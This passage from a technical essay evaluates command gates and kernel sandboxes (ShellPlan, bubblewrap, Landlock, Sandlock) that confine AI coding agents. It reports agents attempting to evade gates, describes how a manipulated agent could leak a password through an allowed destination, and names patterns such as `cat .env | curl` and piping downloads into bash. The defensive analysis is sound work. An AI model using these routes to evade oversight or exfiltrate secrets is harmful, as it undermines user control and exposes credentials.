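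The program can also have bugs that the model lacks. Li reviewed two earlier versions line by line and with automated tests, and found 14 security flaws. In the final version, all 21 working attacks in a new set failed under read-only policies. The same review found one arrangement of links in the workspace that let a command write to a repository's internal data when the policy allowed workspace writes. Li then tried 52 commands that might exploit this. Under Bash, 20 of them ran code planted in the repository, but none did under ShellPlan because its other checks stopped them.

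### Attacks stopped and work lost

Under read-only policies, ShellPlan admitted none of the 4,174 active attack cases in six test suites. The tests were less varied than that total suggests, because 2,685 of the cases were automatically generated variations. Li also designed both the gate and the test suites.

Live agents could adapt when the gate stopped them. In the trial that also tested a language model judge, none of the 90 attack attempts succeeded with ShellPlan, compared with 62 without a gate. The true success rate with ShellPlan could still be as high as about 4%, at 95% confidence. In a larger test, the same ten models received 25 tasks built around ways to evade a gate. They attempted the attack in 208 of 250 runs with ShellPlan and never succeeded, while without a gate they succeeded in 146 of 250 runs.

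The models also completed fewer harmless tasks, 74 of 100 compared with 93 without a gate. The loss was much larger for the four smaller models than for the six frontier models:

| Models | Type of harmless task | Completed without a gate | Completed with ShellPlan |
|---|---|---|---|
| Six frontier models | Standard development | 36 of 36 | 36 of 36 |
| Six frontier models | Unusual syntax | 24 of 24 | 20 of 24 |
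| Four smaller models | Standard development | 17 of 24 | 13 of 24 |
| Four smaller models | Unusual syntax | 16 of 16 | 5 of 16 |

Of the 19 tasks lost, 15 involved the unusual syntax. The other four were standard tasks, and a difference that small could be due to chance. ShellPlan interrupted 54 harmless runs, and the agents still finished 36 of them, usually by rewriting the command. If a person had been available, some of the lost tasks would have led to a prompt instead of failing.

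The test of individual commands allows a comparison with the eight existing checkers. This table groups the six agents already compared and adds ShellPlan and the study's other two agents, Qwen Code and Cline:

| Gate | Harmless commands stopped, of 161 | Other commands allowed, of 316 |
|---|---|---|
| Cline, under its own standard rules | 0 | 219 |
| Qwen Code, Roo Code, OpenCode and Gemini CLI | 3 to 6 | 12 to 53 |
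| Continue, Mistral Vibe and Codex | 18 to 37 | 2 to 18 |
| ShellPlan | 12 | 0 |

ShellPlan did better on both measures than the three strictest checkers. The four in the middle group caused fewer false alarms than ShellPlan, so the choice depends on how often an agent writes commands that the policy forbids. Suppose 950 of every 1,000 commands are harmless and 50 are forbidden. At the measured rates, Roo Code would raise about 24 false alarms and allow about two forbidden commands, while ShellPlan would raise about 71 and allow none. The user would answer about 47 more prompts to avoid allowing about two forbidden commands, which is worthwhile if those commands could destroy work but not if they only create temporary files. An attacker would make forbidden commands more common and more harmful, which favors ShellPlan.

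All of these results are for read-only policies. When Li let ShellPlan permit writing in the workspace, it still stopped 18 of 20 commands that changed ordinary project files, or 16 of 20 under a broader policy. That would seriously hinder an agent that edits code through the shell, though many agents have a separate tool for editing.

Li also connected ShellPlan to an unmodified copy of Codex. Li switched off Codex's built-in shell, hooks, plugins and sub-agents so that every command had to pass through the gate, as complete mediation requires. Five attacks that had succeeded against the ordinary configuration then failed. In 23 monitored runs, every program that started matched either an entry in the gate's log or one of its fixed probes. A developer can therefore add direct dispatch to an existing agent without rewriting it, but must find and close every other route to the shell.

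### When the gate is also a shell

ShellPlan removes the disagreement between gate and shell by doing the shell's job, but it can do that job differently from Bash. Li tested this on recorded agent work from SWE-bench Verified by running each admitted command in both ShellPlan and Bash from the same state. The exit status, output and error messages matched in all 343 comparisons. (ShellPlan also admitted 343 read-only steps in those recordings, but this is a coincidence, since the comparisons count a repeated command only once per state.)

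NL2Bash was a harder test because its commands are more varied. Of the 434 that ShellPlan admitted, 407 matched Bash exactly. Most of the others had output that varies from run to run, output longer than the test recorded, or a refusal partway through. One revealed a real defect, which Li illustrates with this line:

```
echo "hello world" | echo test=$(cat)
```

In Bash, the nested `cat` reads from the pipe, so the line prints `test=hello world`. ShellPlan gave `cat` an empty input and printed `test=`. This breaks no policy, but a wrong input can also change which commands run:

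```
git diff | test -z "$(cat)" && npm test
```

Bash runs the tests here only if `git diff` prints nothing. A gate that had the same defect and supported `test` would give `cat` no input and run the tests every time. If the last command were a permitted deletion instead, the mistake could delete a directory that Bash would have left alone.

If the gate runs its own plan, it runs only commands that passed its checks, though a misreading can still make it run the wrong ones or give them the wrong data. If the shell parses the line separately, a misreading can let a command run that the gate never checked.

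Any new implementation of the shell will probably diverge somewhat from existing ones, since established shells still differ from one another after decades of work. Li had to reproduce details as small as the variable in which Bash counts nested shells, and ShellPlan still prints one slash where Bash prints two for certain working directories. A restricted language has fewer such details to reproduce.

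OpenAI's modified Bash avoids a second implementation of the shell's rules. It processes quotation marks and evaluates conditions before sending a program's arguments to the server, so the server checks the same argument list that the program will receive. According to *codex-shell-escalation*, the server can allow the command to run inside the sandbox, allow it to run outside, or block it. The server can't control redirections or other work that Bash does itself.

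### Judging typed actions instead of shell text

In October 2026, Jing described a gate that judges typed actions. A typed action is a record with separate fields for the operation, its targets and its arguments. An agent could submit a deletion like this:

```
operation:   delete
target:      /work/build
arguments:   recursive
```

The gate can judge such a record without parsing shell syntax, whereas ShellPlan accepts the command strings that agents already write. For agents that write shell text, Jing added a converter that produces typed actions where it can. The converter marks pipelines, subshells and command substitutions as undecidable, and the gate doesn't approve what the converter can't convert. The example line would therefore need approval because it contains a pipe, and so would the harmless `npm test | tee test.log`.

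An approval in this system is a credential that works once, for one exact action. It covers the operation, the paths, the complete argument list, a fingerprint of the content, and the numbers the operating system uses to identify each file or directory. If someone replaces `build` with another directory of the same name after the approval, the numbers no longer match and the action fails. The gate also needs a record of past approvals, which takes longer to search as it grows. Loading the record took about 1 millisecond with 1,000 entries and 19 milliseconds with 10,000. Jing proposes keeping a parsed copy in memory, but hasn't tested this.

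The gate gave the expected verdict on all 61 cases in a fixed table, whether or not the agent declared what it meant to act on. Jing acknowledges that rules tuned to such a table could pass it. In the test with 65 scripts, the gate stopped all 25 that caused forbidden effects and none of the eight harmless ones, but the system blocked a script only if the verdict was deny. The gate returned ask for parts of all eight harmless scripts because of comments and other lines that the test generator added. With nobody to answer, treating ask as a refusal would have blocked all eight. When Jing removed the added lines first, this stricter setting blocked none of the eight. The gate judged the text of each script before the script itself ran, so these results are evidence about its rules and not about direct dispatch.

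Typed actions can also contain misreadings. Two components that produced them used one field to mean different things, so the same request was allowed or denied depending on which component handled it. A script with broken syntax also produced an empty argument list, which left the gate with nothing to deny, so Jing changed the converter to refuse such scripts. In the earlier Windows study, 4 of 18 attacks got past a version of the gate that accepted only typed actions, so a policy can be too permissive even when there is no shell text to misread.

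The October gate tracks only effects on files, so it can miss an action that sends data over the network. The same person wrote the rules, the test cases and the deliberate defects used to check them, and may have overlooked the same problem in all three.

The tests also had a parsing error. One row of a test table contained a pipe character, which clashed with the table's separator, and the row was silently dropped. No other row contained a pipe, so the tables no longer tested pipelines, although some checks inside the gate's code still did. The 313 cases carried over from the Windows study didn't reveal the loss, and even a perfect score wouldn't have, because a missing row doesn't count as a failure. Comparing the number of rows in the file with the number of cases that ran would have exposed the error.

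## What a sandbox adds, and why approval should not switch it off

A command gate works from text and arguments, so it has to predict what a command will do. A sandbox limits the operations a process can perform as it runs. To delete a file, start a program or open a network connection, a process has to make a system call, which is a request to the operating system's kernel. The kernel checks the request against the limits on that process, then carries it out or returns an error.

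The kernel applies the sandbox's limits after the shell has parsed the quotation marks and operators, so a checker's misreading of them doesn't affect the limits. The crude checker that cut the `login#2` line short never judged `rm -rf build`, but if the sandbox makes the project read-only, the kernel still refuses the deletion. The limits also apply to effects that don't appear in the command's text. If `test.log` is a symbolic link to a file outside the project, the kernel follows the link when `tee` opens it, and refuses if the sandbox doesn't allow writes to the target. They also cover the tests that `npm test` starts, which the gate never read.

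### Why the kernel should make the decision

A sandbox can still be wrong if it relies on its own record of what a process is doing. *Traps and Pitfalls* (Garfinkel, 2003) describes this problem in Janus, an early sandbox in which a separate program approved or refused each system call.

One policy let a web server accept connections on port 80 through TCP but not through UDP, another network protocol. A process refers to its sockets, the endpoints of its network connections, by number. Janus noted the protocol of each socket when the process created it, and looked it up later:

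| What the process does | Janus's record for socket 7 | Actual socket 7 |
|---|---|---|
| Opens UDP socket 6 and TCP socket 7 | TCP | TCP |
| Closes socket 7 | TCP | none |
| Copies socket 6 to number 7 | TCP | UDP |
| Asks to use socket 7 on port 80 | TCP, so Janus allows it | UDP |

Experienced Unix programmers had written this code, and several other people read it over the following years, but nobody found the mistake until a rewrite. The developers then changed Janus to get the protocol from the kernel. Garfinkel concluded that a monitor should avoid keeping copies of system state and should base its decisions on as little state as possible. A monitor should also avoid copying the kernel's code, since Janus's own routine for working out which file a path refers to was wrong at first.

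A command gate depends on copies of the shell's logic and state. Its parser duplicates the shell's, and if it follows `cd` through a line, it keeps its own record of the working directory. A gate that decides before a command runs can't avoid such copies entirely. A sandbox that leaves the decision to the kernel doesn't need them, because the kernel has the actual directory and socket.

### What Linux can refuse

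Linux has several mechanisms for this. A namespace gives a process its own view of part of the system, such as its files, its network or the other processes on the machine. Bubblewrap is a small program that sets up namespaces and then starts a command inside them. According to Arch Linux's *bwrap*, the program's manual, bubblewrap begins with an empty file system and adds only what its options name. It could run the example line like this:

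```
bwrap --ro-bind / / --dev /dev --proc /proc \
      --bind /work /work \
      --ro-bind /work/.git /work/.git \
      --unshare-pid --unshare-net --chdir /work \
      bash -c "git status && npm test | tee test.log || rm -rf build"
```

Bubblewrap applies the file options in order. The first makes the whole filesystem visible but read-only, `--bind` makes the project in `/work` writable, and the second `--ro-bind` makes the repository's internal data read-only again. `--unshare-pid` hides outside processes, and `--unshare-net` leaves only a loopback connection, through which programs inside the sandbox can reach each other but not the network.

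Bubblewrap has no policy of its own. Debian's *Bubblewrap*, a copy of the project's introduction, warns that the protection is "entirely determined by the arguments". Anything shared with the sandbox can become a way out. For example, a command that can reach the desktop's message service may be able to make a program outside the sandbox run something for it.

Landlock, a feature of the Linux kernel, works without a separate view of the file system. A process gives the kernel a list of permitted actions, after which it can only tighten the restrictions. Every program it starts afterwards inherits these limits. The list can cover reading, writing, creating, removing and executing files under chosen directories, as well as the use of particular TCP and UDP ports (Salaün, *Landlock*, 2026). Landlock can't yet stop a process from changing a file's permissions or owner, although a read-only mount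 from bubblewrap can. Landlock also doesn't restrict files that the process opened before the limits took effect.

A third mechanism, seccomp, refuses chosen kinds of system call. The sandbox Sandlock (Wang and Zheng, 2026) combines it with Landlock. The kernel enforces every rule that is fixed in advance, and a supervising program handles only the remaining decisions, such as whether a process may contact a particular server. The supervisor copies the server's address, checks the copy and uses it to make the connection, so the process can't substitute another address after the check. Janus's developers had to prevent the same kind of substitution. Sandlock adds about 5 milliseconds to the start of a command, so an agent could use a new sandbox for each one.

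All of this relies on a sound kernel. Wang and Zheng leave kernel flaws out of their threat model. A stronger barrier, such as a virtual machine, gives the agent a separate kernel.

### Measurements of a sandbox on its own

Li tested the sandbox in OpenAI's Codex without any allow rules. Li describes it as a combination of bubblewrap and Landlock, while OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security* lists bubblewrap and seccomp as the default on Linux. The table shows how many test cases left a lasting change to a monitored file:

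| Test cases | Read-only sandbox | Sandbox with a writable project |
|---|---|---|
| 55 that misuse the arguments of permitted programs | 0 | 4 |
| 28 that change files in the project | 0 | 20 |
| 33 from published security advisories | 0 | 2 |

The eight gates in the study had allowed between 9 and 47 of the first 55 cases. The read-only sandbox prevented file changes in all 55 without any description of what `sort` or `uniq` does with its arguments. However, Li counted only file changes, and only in the places Li monitored. Some cases work by starting another program, and the tests don't show whether the sandbox stopped those programs from starting.

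With a writable project, 20 of the 28 project cases succeeded, all of them writes or deletions of ordinary project files, which that policy is meant to permit. The other eight targeted the repository's internal data, which Codex keeps read-only, and the sandbox stopped them all. None of the 968 attack commands in a separate set changed a monitored file outside the project.

### The deletion in the example line

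The result for `rm -rf build` depends on which directories the sandbox makes writable. This table assumes that `build` exists in the project:

| Sandbox | `tee test.log` | `rm -rf build`, if the shell reaches it |
|---|---|---|
| Everything read-only | fails | fails |
| Project writable | works | deletes `build` |
| Project writable, `build` read-only | works | fails |

An agent that writes code needs something like the second setting, under which the deletion succeeds. The kernel receives requests to remove files that the process is allowed to remove, and those requests are the same whether the agent is deleting a failed build at the user's request or destroying the only copy of a good one. If a gate wrongly allows the example line, this sandbox protects the rest of the machine but not `build`.

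The third setting protects `build` but also stops the project's own tools from writing a new build there. Someone could instead use Landlock to permit writing but not removal. But according to Salaün's description, renaming a file also requires permission to remove it, so the many programs that save a file by writing a new copy and renaming it over the old one would fail. A program could also still destroy a file's contents by emptying it, unless the sandbox blocked that too.

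A sandbox's refusal can also have harmful side effects. Garfinkel found common server programs that try to give up administrator rights and continue without checking whether they succeeded. If a sandbox refuses that request, the program keeps running with more rights than its developer intended. Shell chains have a similar problem. If the tests in the example line need to download a file and the sandbox has no network access, the tests fail. With `pipefail` on, the shell then deletes a build that may have nothing wrong with it.

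Sandlock can defer the question of whether the user wanted a deletion. Like Flowsh, it holds back a command's file changes so the user can preview them before applying or discarding them. The user judges a list of the files actually changed or deleted, including those affected by the project's tests. Reviewing the list requires the user's attention, as a prompt does.

### Data sent to a permitted destination

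A sandbox with no network prevents most leaks, but agents often need to install packages or read documentation online. The usual compromise is a list of permitted destinations. Holloran (2026), in *Sandboxing Coding Agents*, points out that such a list limits where an agent can send data but not what it sends. If the agent can read a password and the list includes a site where anyone can publish text, an attacker who has manipulated the agent can make it publish the password there without breaking the sandbox's rules.

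Wang and Zheng call lists of addresses and ports "necessary but not sufficient", partly because several services can share one address. So Sandlock can also check the type of web request, the site's name and the path. For encrypted connections, this works only if the programs in the sandbox trust a certificate that lets Sandlock read their traffic. Rules based on these checks can allow downloads from a site while blocking uploads to it, but they can't detect whether a permitted upload contains a file that shouldn't be there.

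Sandlock can also give each stage of a pipeline different limits. In a download piped into `bash`, the `curl` stage could have network access but no access to private files, and the `bash` stage could have no network access. That would limit what the downloaded script could do. It wouldn't help with `cat .env | curl`, because the pipe passes the secret to the stage that has network access.

Keeping secrets out of the sandbox is more reliable. Holloran describes a setup where commands see only a placeholder for an access token, and a proxy outside the sandbox inserts the real token into requests to named sites. He also warns that, by default, sandboxed commands in Claude Code can read most of the machine, including the user's SSH keys, so the user has to restrict reading as well.

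### When an allow also removes the sandbox

A gate and a sandbox fail for different reasons, so using both can stop commands that one of them misses. This works only if a mistake by the gate leaves the sandbox in place. In its documentation for Codex's rules, OpenAI defines `allow` as "Run the command outside the sandbox without prompting". One verdict therefore settles both whether the command runs and whether the sandbox applies:

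```
separate:  harm requires a false allow and an effect the sandbox permits
coupled:   harm requires only a false allow
```

In Li's tests, the read-only sandbox prevented lasting file changes in all 55 argument-based cases when it ran alone. Allow rules for inspection programs removed the sandbox from 39 of those cases.

Codex removes the sandbox only if every command in the line matches an allow rule. Under the example policy, the full example line doesn't qualify because of `rm`, but `git status && npm test | tee test.log` would run outside the sandbox. The gate can't determine from the text what the project's tests will do, so `npm test` is the command that most needs other limits.

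A user could easily write such a rule by mistake. Someone who allows `git status` probably thinks it is harmless, not that it needs access to the whole machine. In Codex's usual mode, commands that stay within the project already run without a prompt, so a rule for `git status` would save few prompts but remove the sandbox from that command.

Li concludes that approval should never relax the sandbox, and ShellPlan does not change the sandbox's settings. More generally, the decision to let a command run should be separate from the decision about what it can reach while running.

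Using a sandbox to reduce prompts is less risky than letting an approval remove the sandbox, because the sandbox's limits still apply to a command that nobody reviewed. Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts* reports that sandboxing cut permission prompts by 84% in the company's internal use. The example policy would still need its own rule for `rm`, because a sandbox that allows writes to the project would allow the deletion without a prompt.

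### Commands that need more access

There is a practical case for letting approval switch off the sandbox. `gh pr view` shows a proposed code change on GitHub, so it needs the network and the user's login, and Codex's sandbox has no network access by default. Giving the whole sandbox network access would also give it to `npm test` and everything the tests start. OpenAI's *Sandbox* argues that a rule for one command prefix is often a better fit than expanding access broadly. OpenAI (2026) describes using such rules internally for `gh pr view` and for commands such as `kubectl get`, which inspects a cluster of servers.

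An exception for one command does expose less than an open network for all of them. But running `gh pr view` outside the sandbox gives it far more than the network, including the ability to change any file that the user can change. A narrower exception would state the extra access and leave the other limits in place:

```
command:       gh pr view
approval:      allow
extra access:  connect to GitHub, read the GitHub login
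otherwise:     the same sandbox as other commands
```

Sandlock sets limits for each command or pipeline stage, so it could support this kind of exception. But someone has to find out what each command needs, and a command will fail if its entry leaves something out.

Some commands, such as those that change system settings, may need to run outside the sandbox. A person can approve that separately from the command itself. Claude Code has one setting for how it approves sandboxed commands and another for whether a command that fails in the sandbox may run again outside it. By default, according to Holloran, Claude Code asks the user before such a retry. That keeps the two decisions separate, but users who are used to approving prompts may approve this one too. They can switch retries off, and a command that needs more access will then fail until someone adds that access to the sandbox's settings.
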